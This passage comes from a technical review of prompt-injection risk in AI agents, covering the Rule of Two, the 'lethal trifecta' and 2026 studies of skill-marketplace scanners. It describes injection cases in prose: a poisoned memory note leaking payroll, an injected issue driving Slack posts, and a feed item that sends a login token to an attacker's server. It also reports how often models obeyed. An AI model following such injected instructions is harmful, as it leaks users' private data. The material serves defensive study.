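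Meta applies the same reasoning to three other hypothetical agents:

| Agent | Properties it keeps | How the developer restricts the other one |
|---|---|---|
| Travel assistant | A and B | A person confirms each booking or payment, and the agent can't open web addresses it has made up itself |
| Web research assistant | A and C | The browser runs in a sandbox with no saved logins, and the agent gets little private information |
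| Internal programming agent | B and C | A filter admits only data from approved authors, and people review what it wrongly blocks |

The ban on made-up addresses prevents the travel assistant from leaking data through `fetch_page`. The assistant can still follow a link from a trusted search result, but it can't add the user's salary to the end of the link.

Property C covers more than the third part of the lethal trifecta because it includes changing state, such as deleting a record or editing a file. Suppose an agent reads strangers' support tickets and can delete customer accounts, but can't send messages. TF001 wouldn't flag it because the agent can't send data out. TF002 would flag it, and the Rule of Two forbids it from running unsupervised because it has all three properties. Willison (2025), in *Prompt injection*, welcomed the inclusion of state changes because his trifecta covers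 only data theft.

Meta presents the rule as a provisional measure until developers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection. To support the premise that they can't yet do so, Willison cites *The Attacker Moves Second*, a paper published the same month by researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and elsewhere. The researchers tested 12 published defences with attacks adapted to each one. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences, although attack success rates for most of them had originally been reported as near zero.

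### Is a pair of properties safe?

Meta's original diagram labelled every pair of properties "safe". Willison objected that an agent with A and C can do harm without any private data, since a stranger's text can trigger it to make changes. He added that an exception for this pair would spoil the rule's simplicity.

Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that B covers any sensitive system, even one that holds no private data. An agent without B can therefore make only changes that don't matter much to its user, such as changes in a sandbox. Meta also replaced "safe" with "lower risk" in the diagram.

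The reply answers much of the objection. An agent that reads web pages and can pay bills has A and C, and if the payment system counts as sensitive, it also has B and needs supervision. But this means B and C can no longer be judged separately. A developer has to judge how much damage each change could do before deciding whether the agent has two properties or three, and two developers could reasonably disagree. TF002 avoids part of this difficulty because it checks directly whether an action is irreversible.

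Some harms remain under either reading. An agent with A and C could send spam from inside its sandbox, which would hurt the recipients more than the user. An agent with A and B can't send anything out, but an injection could still make it give the user a false answer, such as the wrong bank account for an invoice. Meta acknowledges both gaps and notes that the rule isn't designed to prevent an agent's own mistakes.

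### Sessions and memory

The limit of two applies to a session, but many agents keep notes between sessions. The mbgsec commentary *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) asks whether changing state includes changing the agent's own internal state, which is crucial for an agent with a permanent scratch pad.

Suppose an agent reads a stranger's web page on Monday and saves a note about it. The page contains an injection, so the note includes an instruction to put the payroll in the agent's next report to the stranger's address. On Tuesday, in a new session without web access, the agent reads its notes and the payroll and sends the report. The stranger gets the payroll even though Monday's session had only A and, if saving a note counts, C, and Tuesday's seems to have only B and C.

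The labels from taint tracking resolve this. If the agent writes a note after reading untrusted text, the note is also labeled untrusted and keeps that label on Tuesday, so Tuesday's session has A, B and C. But if the agent often reads the web, almost every note will become untrusted unless a person reviews the notes or the agent keeps separate memories for separate tasks.

Meta also allows an agent to change its pair of properties during a session if doing so breaks the attacker's path. For example, an agent could start with A and C to search the internet, then permanently lose the ability to communicate externally before it accesses internal systems. An injection from the web may still be in its context, but the agent can no longer send anything out.

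The opposite order would be unsafe. If the agent read internal files and then lost access to them before going online, the files' contents would still be in its context when it encountered the injection.

### What to do about a flag

Removing a class of tools is the most reliable remedy, and the smallest class is often a good place to start. The office assistant would lose three tools if the company removed its sinks and five if it removed the tools that read private data. But the company may have wanted the assistant for those three sinks, in which case it has other options.

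**Splitting the agent.** Understanding Data's *The Lethal Trifecta*, a guide for developers, recommends dividing the work so that no single agent holds both private data and untrusted text. The company could give the four untrusted-content tools to a reading agent and the other eight tools to an office agent. Neither agent has a triple by itself. But if the reading agent passes on a free-text summary, the summary can contain an injection, and the office agent then has all three properties. The company could limit the handover to fixed choices, such as a ticket number and one of five categories. This would leave little room for an injection, though a stranger could still influence which category the reading agent picks.

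**Narrowing the destination.** A sink is no longer public if it can reach only people entitled to the data. If the company restricts `send_email` to its own addresses and limits the other two sinks in the same way, the count falls from 60 to 0 without removing a tool. The server or the application has to enforce the list of allowed destinations, because an injection could override an instruction to the model. Someone also has to keep the list up to date, as the expired domain in ForcedLeak showed. If the tool's description doesn't mention the restriction, a scanner may keep flagging the agent, so the owner has to record why the flag no longer applies.

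**Requiring approval.** An agent that needs all three properties can ask a person for approval before it acts. Users may stop reading frequent requests, and Meta lists blind confirmation as a way the rule can fail. Snyk suggests intervening only when the next call would complete a toxic flow. The office assistant could then read reviews and send routine emails without interruption, but it would have to ask before sending anything in a session where it had read both a stranger's text and the payroll. The request should show the full message and the recipient.

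## How often dangerous combinations occur in skill marketplaces

Rules like TF001 flag an agent for what it could do, so their usefulness depends on how many agents they flag and how many of those flags are correct. Two 2026 studies looked for dangerous combinations among thousands of skills on public marketplaces. One tested pairs of skills that each pass a check alone, and a human reviewer accepted about one in five flags. The other found hundreds of single skills with the lethal trifecta but observed no leak through that combination.

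### Pairs of skills that pass alone

Spera's theorem shows that two safe sets of capabilities can form an unsafe one, but not how often this happens with real skills. Wang, Qian and colleagues (2026) measured this in *When Safe Skills Collide* with a scanner called SkillReact. They tried to download all 5,128 skills their crawler found on ClawHub and got 1,520. When they retried 286 of the failed downloads, 269 worked, so the failures probably had more to do with the crawler than with the skills.

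SkillReact searches each skill's instructions and code for signs of eight capabilities, such as reading files, starting other programs and sending data over the network. It then checks the capabilities it detects against ten forbidden combinations. Of the 1,520 skills, 869 matched a forbidden combination on their own. The other 651 passed and form 211,575 pairs (651 × 650 / 2).

For each pair, SkillReact pools the two skills' labels and checks the ten combinations again. It flagged 47,075 pairs, or 22.25%. The table shows how many pairs matched each combination. A pair can match several, so the counts add up to 78,878. The last two columns come from a human audit of a sample.

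| Pattern | Capabilities required | Pairs | Share of matches | Judged valid |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Data exfiltration | read files, send data | 33,708 | 42.7% | 2 of 20 |
| Environment exfiltration | read environment variables, send data | 17,808 | 22.6% | 5 of 20 |
| Credential theft | use credentials, send data | 13,568 | 17.2% | 5 of 20 |
| "Lethal trifecta" | use credentials, read files, send data | 6,996 | 8.9% | 5 of 20 |
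| System reconnaissance | read system information, send data | 2,968 | 3.8% | 3 of 20 |
| Privilege escalation | read environment variables, start programs | 1,176 | 1.5% | 9 of 20 |
| Persistent backdoor | write files, start programs | 1,022 | 1.3% | 5 of 20 |
| Dropper | send data, write files, start programs | 797 | 1.0% | 2 of 20 |
| Lateral movement | use credentials, send data, start programs | 779 | 1.0% | 2 of 20 |
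| Reverse shell | receive connections, start programs | 56 | 0.1% | 1 of 20 |

The large numbers come from multiplication, as with the office assistant's 60 triples. A skill that could both read files and send data would have failed when checked alone, so every data exfiltration pair has one skill that reads and another that sends. The published counts imply that 159 of the 651 skills can read files and 212 can send data, which gives 159 × 212 = 33,708 pairs. If SkillReact wrongly labels one skill as able to send data, that error can create up to 159 false pairs under this pattern alone.

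Users also install more than two skills. Someone who picked ten of the 651 at random would have about a 92% chance of getting at least one that reads files and one that sends data. Real users don't choose at random, but if a warning appears on most people's machines, they have little reason to act on it.

### How the audit arrived at 18.2%

Wang and colleagues randomly sampled 20 matches for each pattern, 200 in all. Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.5 judged each match, and then a human reviewer made the final decision. A match was valid if both skills really had the capabilities and the harm was plausible in some workflow. The reviewer accepted 39 of the 200, or 19.5%.

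That simple average treats all patterns as equally common, although data exfiltration has about 600 times as many matches as reverse shell. The researchers therefore multiplied each pattern's acceptance rate by its share of all matches:

0.427 × 0.10 + 0.226 × 0.25 + 0.172 × 0.25 + … = 0.182

The weighted rate, which is the precision of SkillReact's matches, is 18.2%, with a 95% interval from 11.3% to 27.4%. The researchers call the 22.25% a ceiling on the number of risky pairs, but they audited only flagged matches, so they did not measure how many risky pairs the scanner missed.

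The weighted rate depends heavily on a few decisions. Each decision about a data exfiltration match moves it by 2.1 percentage points, while a decision about a reverse shell match hardly moves it. If the reviewer had accepted four data exfiltration matches instead of two, the rate would have been 22.5%. A sample of 20 is too small for a precise estimate, because 2 acceptances are compatible with a true rate anywhere between about 1% and 32%.

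The reviewer also saw both models' answers before deciding. The models agreed with each other on 159 of the 200 matches, and the reviewer upheld all 159 of those answers. The models may have been right each time, or the reviewer may have relied on them. Wang and colleagues acknowledge this problem. They recommend adding a second reviewer and having reviewers decide before seeing the models' answers.

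### Why 4.05% of pairs is a projection

Multiplying the two rates (0.182 × 22.25%) gives an estimate that 4.05% of all pairs, or about 8,567, are risky. Wang and colleagues report this figure as a projection because the reviewer judged matches, not pairs.

One pair of skills can account for several of the 78,878 matches. For example, if one skill reads files and uses credentials and another sends data, the pair matches data exfiltration, credential theft and the "lethal trifecta", so it appears three times. Flagged pairs average 1.68 matches, so a hundred of them would have 168 matches, of which about 31 would be valid. The number of risky pairs would be 31 if each valid match belonged to a different pair, but only about 10 if each risky pair had three valid matches.

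Scaling the two cases up to all 211,575 pairs gives 6.78% and about 2.3%. The 4.05% figure is based on the assumption that the valid share is the same for pairs as for matches. To test this, the reviewer would have to judge each sampled pair against every pattern it matches.

### How reliable the labels are

SkillReact assigns labels with regular expressions (text search patterns). It labels a skill as able to send data if it finds, for example, a web address, the command `curl` or a phrase like "call an API". This is fast and gives the same result every time, but the patterns also match documentation, so a sentence such as "no API keys needed" can give a skill the credentials label. The matching text was within 40 characters of a negative word in 9.2% of the evidence behind the flagged pairs, and in 26.4% of the evidence for the ability to start programs.

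To check the labels, the researchers had Claude Sonnet 4.6 label 50 of the skills independently. They measured agreement with Cohen's kappa, which allows for the agreement two raters would reach by chance:

κ = (observed agreement − chance agreement) / (1 − chance agreement)

A kappa of 1 means perfect agreement, and 0 means agreement no better than chance. The average over the eight capabilities was 0.17. If two raters each gave a label to half of the skills, they would agree on 50% of the skills by chance and on 58.5% with a kappa of 0.17.

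Agreement, measured by kappa, was best for sending data (0.50) and very poor for reading files (0.03). A pair is a real risk only if both labels are right, so the unreliable file-reading label may explain why the reviewer accepted only 2 of the 20 data exfiltration matches. But kappa doesn't show which rater was wrong, and Sonnet surely made some of the mistakes.

### Whether models act on a flagged pair

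Wang and colleagues also ran 27 trials with injected prompts, and no model made a forbidden tool call. This is encouraging, but the sample is small. Even if 3% of injections worked, as in the public competition described earlier, all 27 would fail 44% of the time.

In another test, the researchers gave six models the same harmful request and changed only which skills the models saw.

| Skills shown to the models | Complied |
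|---|---|
| None | 17 of 18 |
| An unrelated pair | 12 of 18 |
| The flagged pair | 11 of 18 |

The flagged pair didn't make the models more willing to comply. If anything, extra text about skills seems to have made them less willing. But the request stated the harmful action openly, and the models had no tools and only had to answer in writing. The test therefore measured their willingness but not their ability to carry out the request, which is what a combination adds.

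Xie, Du and colleagues (2026), in *Benign in Isolation, Harmful in Composition*, tested that ability more directly. They built 150 cases in which one skill finds a target and another can act on it, for example by changing who has access to a file. When the agent had both skills, an average of 33.6% of runs across nine models ended in harm, with rates ranging from 0% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 91.5% for DeepSeek-V4. The average was 1.4% with only the acting skill, and zero with only the finding skill or neither. Zheng, Li and colleagues (2026), in *CoSA*, likewise found that adding a few individually vetted skills raised policy violations from 35.02% to 58.45% on the same tasks.

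Combinations can therefore matter a lot when the skills fit together. But both teams chose skills that would fit together, so their rates don't apply to pairs picked at random from a marketplace.

Attempts to exploit random pairs of skills usually fail. In *Detecting Insecure Compositions of Clean Agent Skills via Capability-Flow Graph Analysis*, Li, Fu and colleagues (2026) matched broad risk tags across 1,062 popular ClawHub skills and found 829,462 links, more than one per pair on average. They tried to exploit 500 of these links on each of three agent programs, and 16.5% of the attempts succeeded, ranging from 1.6% on OpenCode to 40.8% on Hermes. This average isn't directly comparable to SkillReact's 18.2%, because it counts successful attacks, whereas SkillReact's reviewer judged whether a harm was plausible.

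Li and colleagues kept only the links with evidence that an agent could pass data from one skill to the next, which left 13 chains of skills. All 13 worked on at least one of the agent programs. Gandhi and colleagues' scanner also looks for such links, including files that two skills share.

### Skills that hold the whole trifecta

A single skill can complete the trifecta. SkillReact's pairs exclude most such skills because they fail when checked individually. In *Beyond Maliciousness*, Pandey, Singh and colleagues (2026) looked for them among 6,309 listings from the ClawHub and skillsmp marketplaces. They found 628 (10.0%) with private data access, untrusted content and a way to send data out, and 397 (6.3%) with both credential access and outbound network access.

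To infer these capabilities, the researchers had language models read every file in each skill, including the scripts. Claude Haiku 4.5 read 5,791 of the listings and Claude Sonnet 4.6 read the rest. The models produced 70 different capability labels, which the researchers merged into 11 groups. A model that reads whole files can distinguish the phrase "no API keys needed" from a script that opens a key file, so it should avoid some of SkillReact's mistakes. But the study's human checks covered malicious intent rather than capabilities, so the precision of the 628 trifecta flags is unknown.

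The count also depends on how the analyst labels shell access. Half of the listings appeared able to run shell commands, and a shell can supply all three parts of the trifecta, as in the `run_command` example. Giving every such listing all three labels would raise the count from 628 trifectas to over 3,000.

Credential access combined with network access is an even weaker sign of danger, because most skills that use an online service need a key to log in and a connection to reach it. About 13% of listings had credential access and 31% could send data. If the two were unrelated, about 250 listings would have both, but 397 did, which suggests that they tend to occur together.

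The 628 listings with the trifecta had a possible route for data to leave, but Pandey and colleagues report, "No leakage was observed." They also mention three runs in which an agent using a skill attempted outbound activity that they classed as exfiltration, but they don't link these runs to the 628 listings. Their scanner judged fewer listings, 338 of the 6,309, malicious or suspicious.

A marketplace can't rely on authors to declare what their skills can do. The skill format has an optional field for tools that the agent may use without asking the user, but only 770 of the 6,061 listings with readable settings used it, and 457 of those understated what the skill could do. Reading the files is slower, but it doesn't depend on the author's honesty or care.

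The percentages describe only this sample, not whole marketplaces, because the researchers left out the most and least popular skills and one publisher accounts for 266 of the listings. Three of the five researchers work for Metano Labs, which built the scanner, and the individual results aren't public. An earlier paper, *Parasites in the Toolchain* (2025), found that 27.2% of MCP servers had at least one tool that could serve a step in this kind of attack.

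### Why reading a skill and running it give different results

Pandey and colleagues also ran all but three of the listings in a sandbox, which recorded programs, tool calls and network activity while an agent used each skill. For most listings, another model, usually Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview, then judged the record. The table shows how many listings had at least one risk finding under each method.

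| Risk found by | Listings |
|---|---|
| Both methods | 978 |
| Reading only | 1,653 |
| Sandbox only | 708 |

The two methods agreed on only 29% of the listings that either one flagged. Much of the disagreement comes from what each can detect. The sandbox, like any runtime analysis, misses scripts that the agent never runs. For example, one group of skills includes a setup script that changes the agent's permanent settings, but the agent never ran it because none of the skills' files mentions it. Reading the skills also flagged 703 listings for depending on unvetted outside software, while the sandbox flagged one.

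The sandbox is better at detecting behaviour that depends on what happens during the run, such as whether the agent passes private data to another service. But its results don't always show whether the skill or the agent caused the behaviour. Most listings ran once, with no comparison run without the skill. In the smaller group that had one, the agent used the shell and read environment variables every time, even without the skill.

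The sandbox recorded shell commands for 518 listings, about one in twelve, although half of the listings appeared able to run them. It also recorded environment reads for 518 listings, and Sonnet 4.6 read exactly 518 listings. This coincidence suggests that the shell count may depend more on how the researchers recorded one batch of runs than on what the skills did.

The scanner's verdicts aren't always repeatable either. When the researchers scanned 89 listings again, 84% got the same verdict and about 14 listings got a different one. The scanner labels a listing suspicious at a score of 0.50 and malicious at 0.70, so a small change in score near either threshold can change the verdict. Most of the changes were of this kind, although two listings went from benign to flagged.

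These verdicts are about malicious intent, so the 84% doesn't show whether a second scan would find the same 628 trifectas. It also doesn't measure accuracy, because a scanner that repeated every mistake would score 100%.

### Two different counts called a trifecta

Both studies use Willison's term, but they count different things.

| | Wang and colleagues | Pandey and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| What they count | pairs of skills that each pass alone | single listings |
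| Private data | credentials and files, both required | any private data |
| Untrusted content | left out | required |
| Way to send data | required | required |
| Result | 6,996 of 211,575 pairs (3.3%) | 628 of 6,309 listings (10.0%) |

The two percentages can't show whether trifectas are more common in pairs or in single skills, mainly because Wang and colleagues treat untrusted content as part of how an attack arrives and not as a capability of a skill. One argument for this choice is that many agents can read web pages or emails whatever skills the user installs. Such an agent already has a tool in U, so only S and X depend on the skills.

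But without U, SkillReact also flags agents that no outsider can steer, which TF001 would clear. The 18.2% is therefore the precision of a broader rule, and it doesn't show how well TF001 would do on the same skills. To measure that, a reviewer would have to record where each agent's text comes from as well as what its skills can do.

### How seldom three scanners agree

ClawHub checks each skill with three kinds of scanner. *ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera et al., 2026) compared the scanners' results on 67,453 skills. The table also shows how each scanner did on the skills that ClawHub's final automated review called suspicious or malicious.

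| Scanner | What it examines | Skills flagged | Share of suspicious skills flagged | Share of malicious skills flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | files, using about 70 antivirus and reputation services | 5,225 | 12.7% | 72.8% |
| Static analysis | risky patterns in code and text | 4,434 | 12.0% | 12.6% |
| SkillSpector | instructions and declared capabilities, partly with a language model | 32,856 | 75.3% | 6.8% |

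The three scanners flagged 35,600 skills between them, but all three flagged only 468, or 0.69% of all skills scanned. For 81.9% of the flagged skills, only one scanner raised a flag. The overlap between any two scanners was at most 10.4% of the skills that either had flagged, and kappa ranged from 0.045 to 0.082.

The 10.4% overlap between SkillSpector and static analysis makes them look further apart than they are. SkillSpector flagged over seven times as many skills as static analysis, so the overlap could not have exceeded 13.5%. SkillSpector flagged 79% of the skills that static analysis flagged. But it also flagged nearly half of all skills, so many of these agreements would have happened by chance. Kappa stays low because it corrects for chance agreement.

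The scanners also look for different things. VirusTotal detects known malware in files, while SkillSpector looks for instructions that give the agent too much authority. A skill with harmless code can include instructions to post private notes to a website, and one with modest instructions can include a program that steals passwords. Koc and colleagues conclude that a marketplace shouldn't decide which skills to allow based on any single scanner. They work for the foundation behind ClawHub and for NVIDIA, which makes SkillSpector, so both organisations had an interest in the comparison.

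The comparison can't show which scanner was right, because a language model made ClawHub's final decisions. *After the Party* (Xiong and Zhang, 2026) added human judgement. Two reviewers labelled 180 ClawHub skills without seeing the scanners' results, then discussed their disagreements. They flagged any skill that raised a definite concern a person should look into, even if the skill wasn't malicious. The first three rows below give the published rates for ClawHub's scanners, weighted to the 276 skills the sample came from. The last row follows from those rates.

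| Scanner | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Language-model scanner | 67% | 61% |
| Static analysis | 75% | 22% |
| VirusTotal | 51% | 25% |
| Any of the three | 57% | 65% |

Adding the other two scanners to the language-model scanner raises recall by only about four points and lowers precision by ten. The reviewers would have flagged 24% of the skills that no scanner flagged. The 276 skills were those whose files the researchers could match exactly to an archived copy, so the rates may differ for the rest of ClawHub.

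The share of skills flagged also varies widely between marketplaces. Holzbauer, Schmidt and colleagues (2026), in *Context Matters*, found that it was 46.8% on ClawHub, 23% on Skills.sh and 6% on SkillsDirectory, which use different scanners. They then checked 2,887 cases in which scanners had flagged a skill to see whether its behaviour made sense given the rest of its GitHub repository. Only 15 cases (0.52%) still looked suspicious.

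That is far below the 51% to 75% precision that Xiong and Zhang measured, largely because the two teams asked different questions. A skill that backs up files to a cloud service may fit its repository, so Holzbauer and colleagues would clear it. But the skill can still read private files and send them over the network, so an agent that uses it and also reads strangers' emails would have all three parts of the trifecta.

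## Checking the links between skills: a scanner from Ben-Gurion University

Two skills can together have every capability an attacker needs and still be harmless if nothing passes from one to the other. SkillReact, which checks only capabilities, flagged 22.25% of the pairs that Wang and colleagues tested. In October 2026, Gandhi and colleagues at Ben-Gurion University described a scanner that also looks for a link, meaning evidence that something one skill produces can reach the other. It did very well on the only public benchmark of labelled skill combinations. But the leaks it found in public repositories passed through the model, where links are hardest to prove.

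### A graph of installed skills

The scanner builds a graph in which each installed skill is a node. An arrow from one skill to another means that the second may receive something from the first. The scanner finds three kinds of arrow by reading scripts, declarations and instructions:

- **Shared file:** one skill writes a file and the other reads the same path.
- **Environment variable:** one skill sets a variable that the other reads.
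- **Named invocation:** one skill calls the other by name.

The scanner usually doesn't match two skills on a bare filename such as `report.txt` alone, since unrelated skills may each have a file with that name. The two skills must also declare the same workspace or a similar shared setting. An arrow gets high confidence only if the names match exactly and both ends come from code or a formal declaration. If one end comes from a sentence in the instructions, the arrow gets low confidence.

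The scanner also labels each skill's capabilities. The main labels are egress (the skill sends data to an outside address), untrusted input (it reads from the network, for example), sensitive data (it reads files or variables on a list of sensitive ones) and shell (it runs commands).

For each file or variable arrow, the scanner then checks what the receiving skill does with the content. It finds the line that reads the file and follows the value through the script, as in the `forward_ticket` trace. It checks whether the script passes the value to an interpreter as code, passes it to a command as an argument, gives it to the agent as instructions, or uses it as the address of a web request. A skill that only counts the words in the file does none of these things.

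### Seven rules

The scanner searches the graph with seven rules. In this table, a context link runs through the model, with no shared file or variable.

| Rule | What the scanner has to find |
|---|---|
| Data exfiltration | A path from a skill with sensitive data to a skill with egress |
| Sensitive consumption | A file or variable link whose receiver puts the content to one of the four uses |
| Input reachability | A path from untrusted input that ends in one of the four uses or in a context link |
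| Target hand-off | A path of context links from a skill that identifies targets to one that acts on targets |
| Decision hand-off | A path of context links from a skill that makes a decision to one whose actions the decision covers |
| Permission mismatch | A skill that invokes another whose permissions are unknown or go beyond its own |
| Undeclared capabilities | A skill that does something its declared permissions leave out |

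The data exfiltration rule doesn't depend on the use check, and the four uses don't include the body of a web request, so the rule can match even when no skill passes on a secret. Suppose one skill reads a private key and writes the time it finished to `status.txt`, and another reads that file but sends only its own version number to its developer. The graph contains a path from sensitive data to egress, although the key never leaves the first skill.

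A validation step is supposed to remove such cases. A language model has to quote lines showing that the first skill produces the content, that the second uses it, and that the agent can pass it between them without the user choosing that value. The model also has to show that the result goes beyond what the user authorised. The scanner checks the quotations against the files and rejects the finding if none of them match.

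### The backup skill and the debugging skill

The backup and debugging skills described earlier, an example from Gandhi and colleagues, share a cache folder. Suppose the folder is `/tmp/cache` and the archive of private keys is `keys.zip`. The scanner would handle the pair as follows:

1. The backup skill reads `~/.ssh`, so it gets the sensitive data label.
2. The debugging skill posts to a public site, so it gets the egress label.
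3. The backup skill writes `/tmp/cache/keys.zip` and the debugging skill reads from `/tmp/cache`, so the scanner draws an arrow between them.
4. The arrow leads from sensitive data to egress, so the data exfiltration rule matches.

The third step is the weak one because the debugging skill uploads whatever it finds in the folder and never names the archive. An exact comparison of `/tmp/cache/keys.zip` with `/tmp/cache` fails, so the scanner would need its optional setting for matching by folder, which gives a low-confidence arrow. If the script worked out the folder's name while running, the scanner would draw the arrow only if a language model suggested it.

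The exfiltration rule's severity is high by default and rises to critical if a skill on the path reads untrusted content and every arrow has high confidence. Neither skill here reads web pages, so the severity stays high, even though the attack begins with a web page. Like SkillReact, the rule assumes that an attacker has some way to reach the agent.

Knowing how two skills are linked can also help the user separate them, which a list of capabilities doesn't. The user could keep both skills and give the debugging skill its own folder. But an injected instruction could still make an agent with shell access copy the archive into the new folder, and neither skill's code would contain that step.

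### Links that exist only in the model's context

In the payroll example, the data passed from one tool to the other only through the model. Connecting every skill to every other would raise too many flags, so the scanner tries to pick out the likely connections in two ways.

The first way of finding links uses fixed rules about what a skill returns and accepts. For example, a skill that lists inactive accounts returns account names, and a skill that removes access takes an account name. The scanner connects them if they also share vocabulary or refer to each other. In the second way, a language model reads the skills' instructions and proposes links the fixed rules missed, with a reason for each.

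A reviewer can check a file link by comparing two lines of code. For a context link, often the only evidence is that one skill produces the kind of output the other could use. Whether an agent would pass that output on depends on the model, the task and the attack. The scanner assigns low confidence to every link that the language model proposes.

KnotScryer, the tool that Li and colleagues used to find the 13 working chains of popular skills, has a more explicit test for context links. It draws a link only if the agent can see the first skill's output, the agent can supply the second skill's input, the data types fit, and the files contain evidence for both ends. In a larger set of 13,598 skills that ClawHub had marked clean, it found 612 chains. The attacks succeeded in 79.2% of tests on average across nine combinations of agent program and model.

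When Li and colleagues dropped the condition that the agent can see the output, the number of chains rose from 13 to 126, and the success rate fell to 40.0%. One false link started from a security log that the agent never sees. However, KnotScryer doesn't cover data that passes through shared files without the agent seeing it, so it could miss the backup and debugging skills.

### Results on SCR-Bench

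Xie and colleagues built SCR-Bench to test whether skills that are harmless alone do damage together. The benchmark has three parts:

- **Capability flow** contains the 150 pairs described earlier, in which one skill finds a target and another acts on it. A run counts as harmful only if the second skill changes the same target that the first one found.
- **Trust transfer** contains 401 cases in which a review skill endorses a harmful skill before the agent decides whether to install it. The endorsement raised the average installation rate across five models from 1.1% to 83.9%.
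- **Authorisation confusion** contains 118 decisions in which the agent may mistake advice for permission. Strongly worded advice raised the rate of risky approvals from 15.7% to 34.0% across ten models.

Gandhi and colleagues used the cases to test scanners that don't run the skills. The test had 668 risky sets of skills and 657 harmless ones, which included the benchmark's own controls and sets made by shuffling skills between unrelated cases. For comparison, they ran SkillsGuard, an existing scanner that examines a folder of skills as a whole, and a language model that read the same files without a graph.

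| Method | Risky sets found (of 668) | False alarms (of 657) | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ben-Gurion scanner | 665 | 9 | 98.7% | 99.6% |
| SkillsGuard, text patterns | 551 | 71 | 88.6% | 82.5% |
| SkillsGuard, language model (lower threshold) | 663 | 214 | 75.6% | 99.3% |
| Language model alone | 657 | 362 | 64.5% | 98.4% |

The language model alone found nearly all the risky sets but also flagged 55% of the harmless ones. Asking for a specific path between skills seems to prevent most of these false alarms.

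The researchers then switched off parts of the scanner and averaged five runs of each version. They left out the trust transfer cases, so this test had 267 risky sets and 218 harmless ones.

| How the scanner finds links | Recall | Harmless sets flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed rules | 54.7% | 0% |
| Fixed rules and language model | 99.2% | 7.0% |
| Fixed rules and language model, then validation | 95.4% | 2.4% |

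The fixed rules found none of the authorisation cases, where one skill passes advice to another. The 146 risky sets they did find must therefore all be among the 150 capability flow pairs, where one skill passes a target to another. Without the fixed rules for context links, the language model still reached a recall of 98.9%, so those rules added only 0.3 points. However, they give the same answer every time and raised no false alarms here.

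The last row suggests that the headline recall is a little high. The version with validation missed about 12 of the 267 sets on average, while the headline run missed at most 3.

### How far the benchmark resembles real use

SCR-Bench mostly tests harms other than data theft. Trust transfer cases, which concern installing a harmful skill, make up 60% of the risky sets. The capability flow pairs include changes to file permissions, devices and network settings. The 98.7% precision covers all these cases, so it doesn't measure how often the data exfiltration rule is right.

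The benchmark also hardly tests the scanner's check for file links, because its skills mainly pass information to each other through the agent's context. That check is the part of the scanner that would catch the backup and debugging skills.

Another concern is that the scanner's rules resemble the benchmark's categories. The target hand-off rule describes the capability flow pairs, and the decision hand-off rule covers a skill that installs another after approving it, as in the trust transfer cases. Gandhi and colleagues define the rules by what skills do, without naming particular skills, so the rules may well work beyond this benchmark. Running the scanner on another team's benchmark, with different kinds of interaction, would test this.

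Xie and colleagues warn that their controlled skills, which act on mock files and services, lack the variety of a real marketplace and the restrictions of real agent programs. The labels also don't reflect differences between models. All 150 capability flow pairs are labeled risky, although Claude Opus 4.5 never did harm with them when the request didn't tell it to combine the two skills.

### Two composite findings in public repositories

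The researchers also ran the scanner on the 1,587 public skills, which form about 1.26 million pairs. After the analysts' review, two composite findings remained, each involving two skills. The researchers don't say how many candidates the analysts rejected, so the scanner's precision can't be calculated from this result.

One finding involves a skill that searches past conversations and a skill that posts to Slack, a workplace chat service. If the agent once read a GitHub issue with a hidden instruction and the user later searches that conversation, the history skill returns the instruction word for word. The agent may then follow it and post private text to Slack. The two skills come from different developers, share no file or variable, and don't call each other. The fixed rules produced no arrow between them, so it had to come from the language model.

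In the other finding, one skill monitors news feeds and another uses a stored login token to test connections. An attacker can publish a feed item containing an instruction for the agent to test a connection to the attacker's server, and the second skill then sends the token there.

The researchers attacked both pairs in a sandbox with fake secrets, using agents that could run shell commands without asking for approval. With the Slack pair, GPT-5.2-Codex followed the instruction in 2 of 12 runs and GLM-5 in 7 of 12. With the other pair, GPT-5.2-Codex leaked the token in 5 of 12 runs and GLM-5 in 6 of 12. Newer models may resist these attacks more often.

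The scanner also recommends repairs. For the Slack pair, it compared eight other Slack skills and chose one that sends messages through an MCP tool with its own approval setting. The user can then approve each Slack message without having to approve every shell command. For 47 of the 55 findings (53 single-skill and two composite), the recommended repairs blocked the attack in all three trials and kept the skill's normal task working.

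### What data-flow checks add to pattern checks

The scanner's 53 confirmed findings about single skills give a first idea of what data-flow checks contribute.

| Check | Reported | Confirmed |
|---|---|---|
| Following values through code | 17 | 14 |
| Text patterns | 2 | 2 |
| Language model reading the instructions | 40 | 37 |

One skill took a folder path from a local server and put it into a shell command unchanged. Both steps are common in harmless scripts, and the flaw is in passing the value from one to the other. A pattern broad enough to catch this would also flag many safe commands. But the table doesn't show how many of the 14 findings another check would have caught without value tracking.

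*Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (Bhardwaj, 2026) appears to support the opposite conclusion. It tested a scanner called SkillFortify on 270 malicious skills generated for the test. Text patterns caught 250 of them. The scanner's information-flow rule fired 44 times, always on skills that the patterns had already caught, so it did not improve recall.

The rule checks whether a skill contains both base64 encoding (a way of writing data as ordinary letters and digits) and an outside network address. Despite its name, it doesn't follow a value through the code, so it could flag a skill that decodes an image and separately fetches a weather forecast, and it would miss one that posts an unencoded key. The result is therefore weak evidence about real taint tracking.

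Every generated skill with this combination also contained a known pattern, so Bhardwaj leaves open whether the technique or the test set is responsible. SkillFortify missed 20 skills, 12 of which relied on a misleading or conflicting name that no data-flow analysis could detect.

Gandhi and colleagues tested all their fixed checks together on 556 skills, 390 of them labelled malicious or suspicious, but didn't test value tracking separately from patterns. The fixed checks alone had a recall of 68.2% and flagged 27.7% of the harmless skills. A language model followed by validation had a recall of 95.8%, and adding the fixed checks raised this to 96.0%, a gain of about one skill.

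Data-flow checks may reduce false alarms more than they improve recall. *Cloak and Detonate* (2026) describes a detector that runs skills in a sandbox. Without taint tracking, the detector caught 95.8% of malicious skills, down from 96.7%, but its false-positive rate rose from 2% to 16%. It could no longer distinguish a skill that reads a sensitive file and uses the network from one that sends the file out.

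### Where static analysis stops

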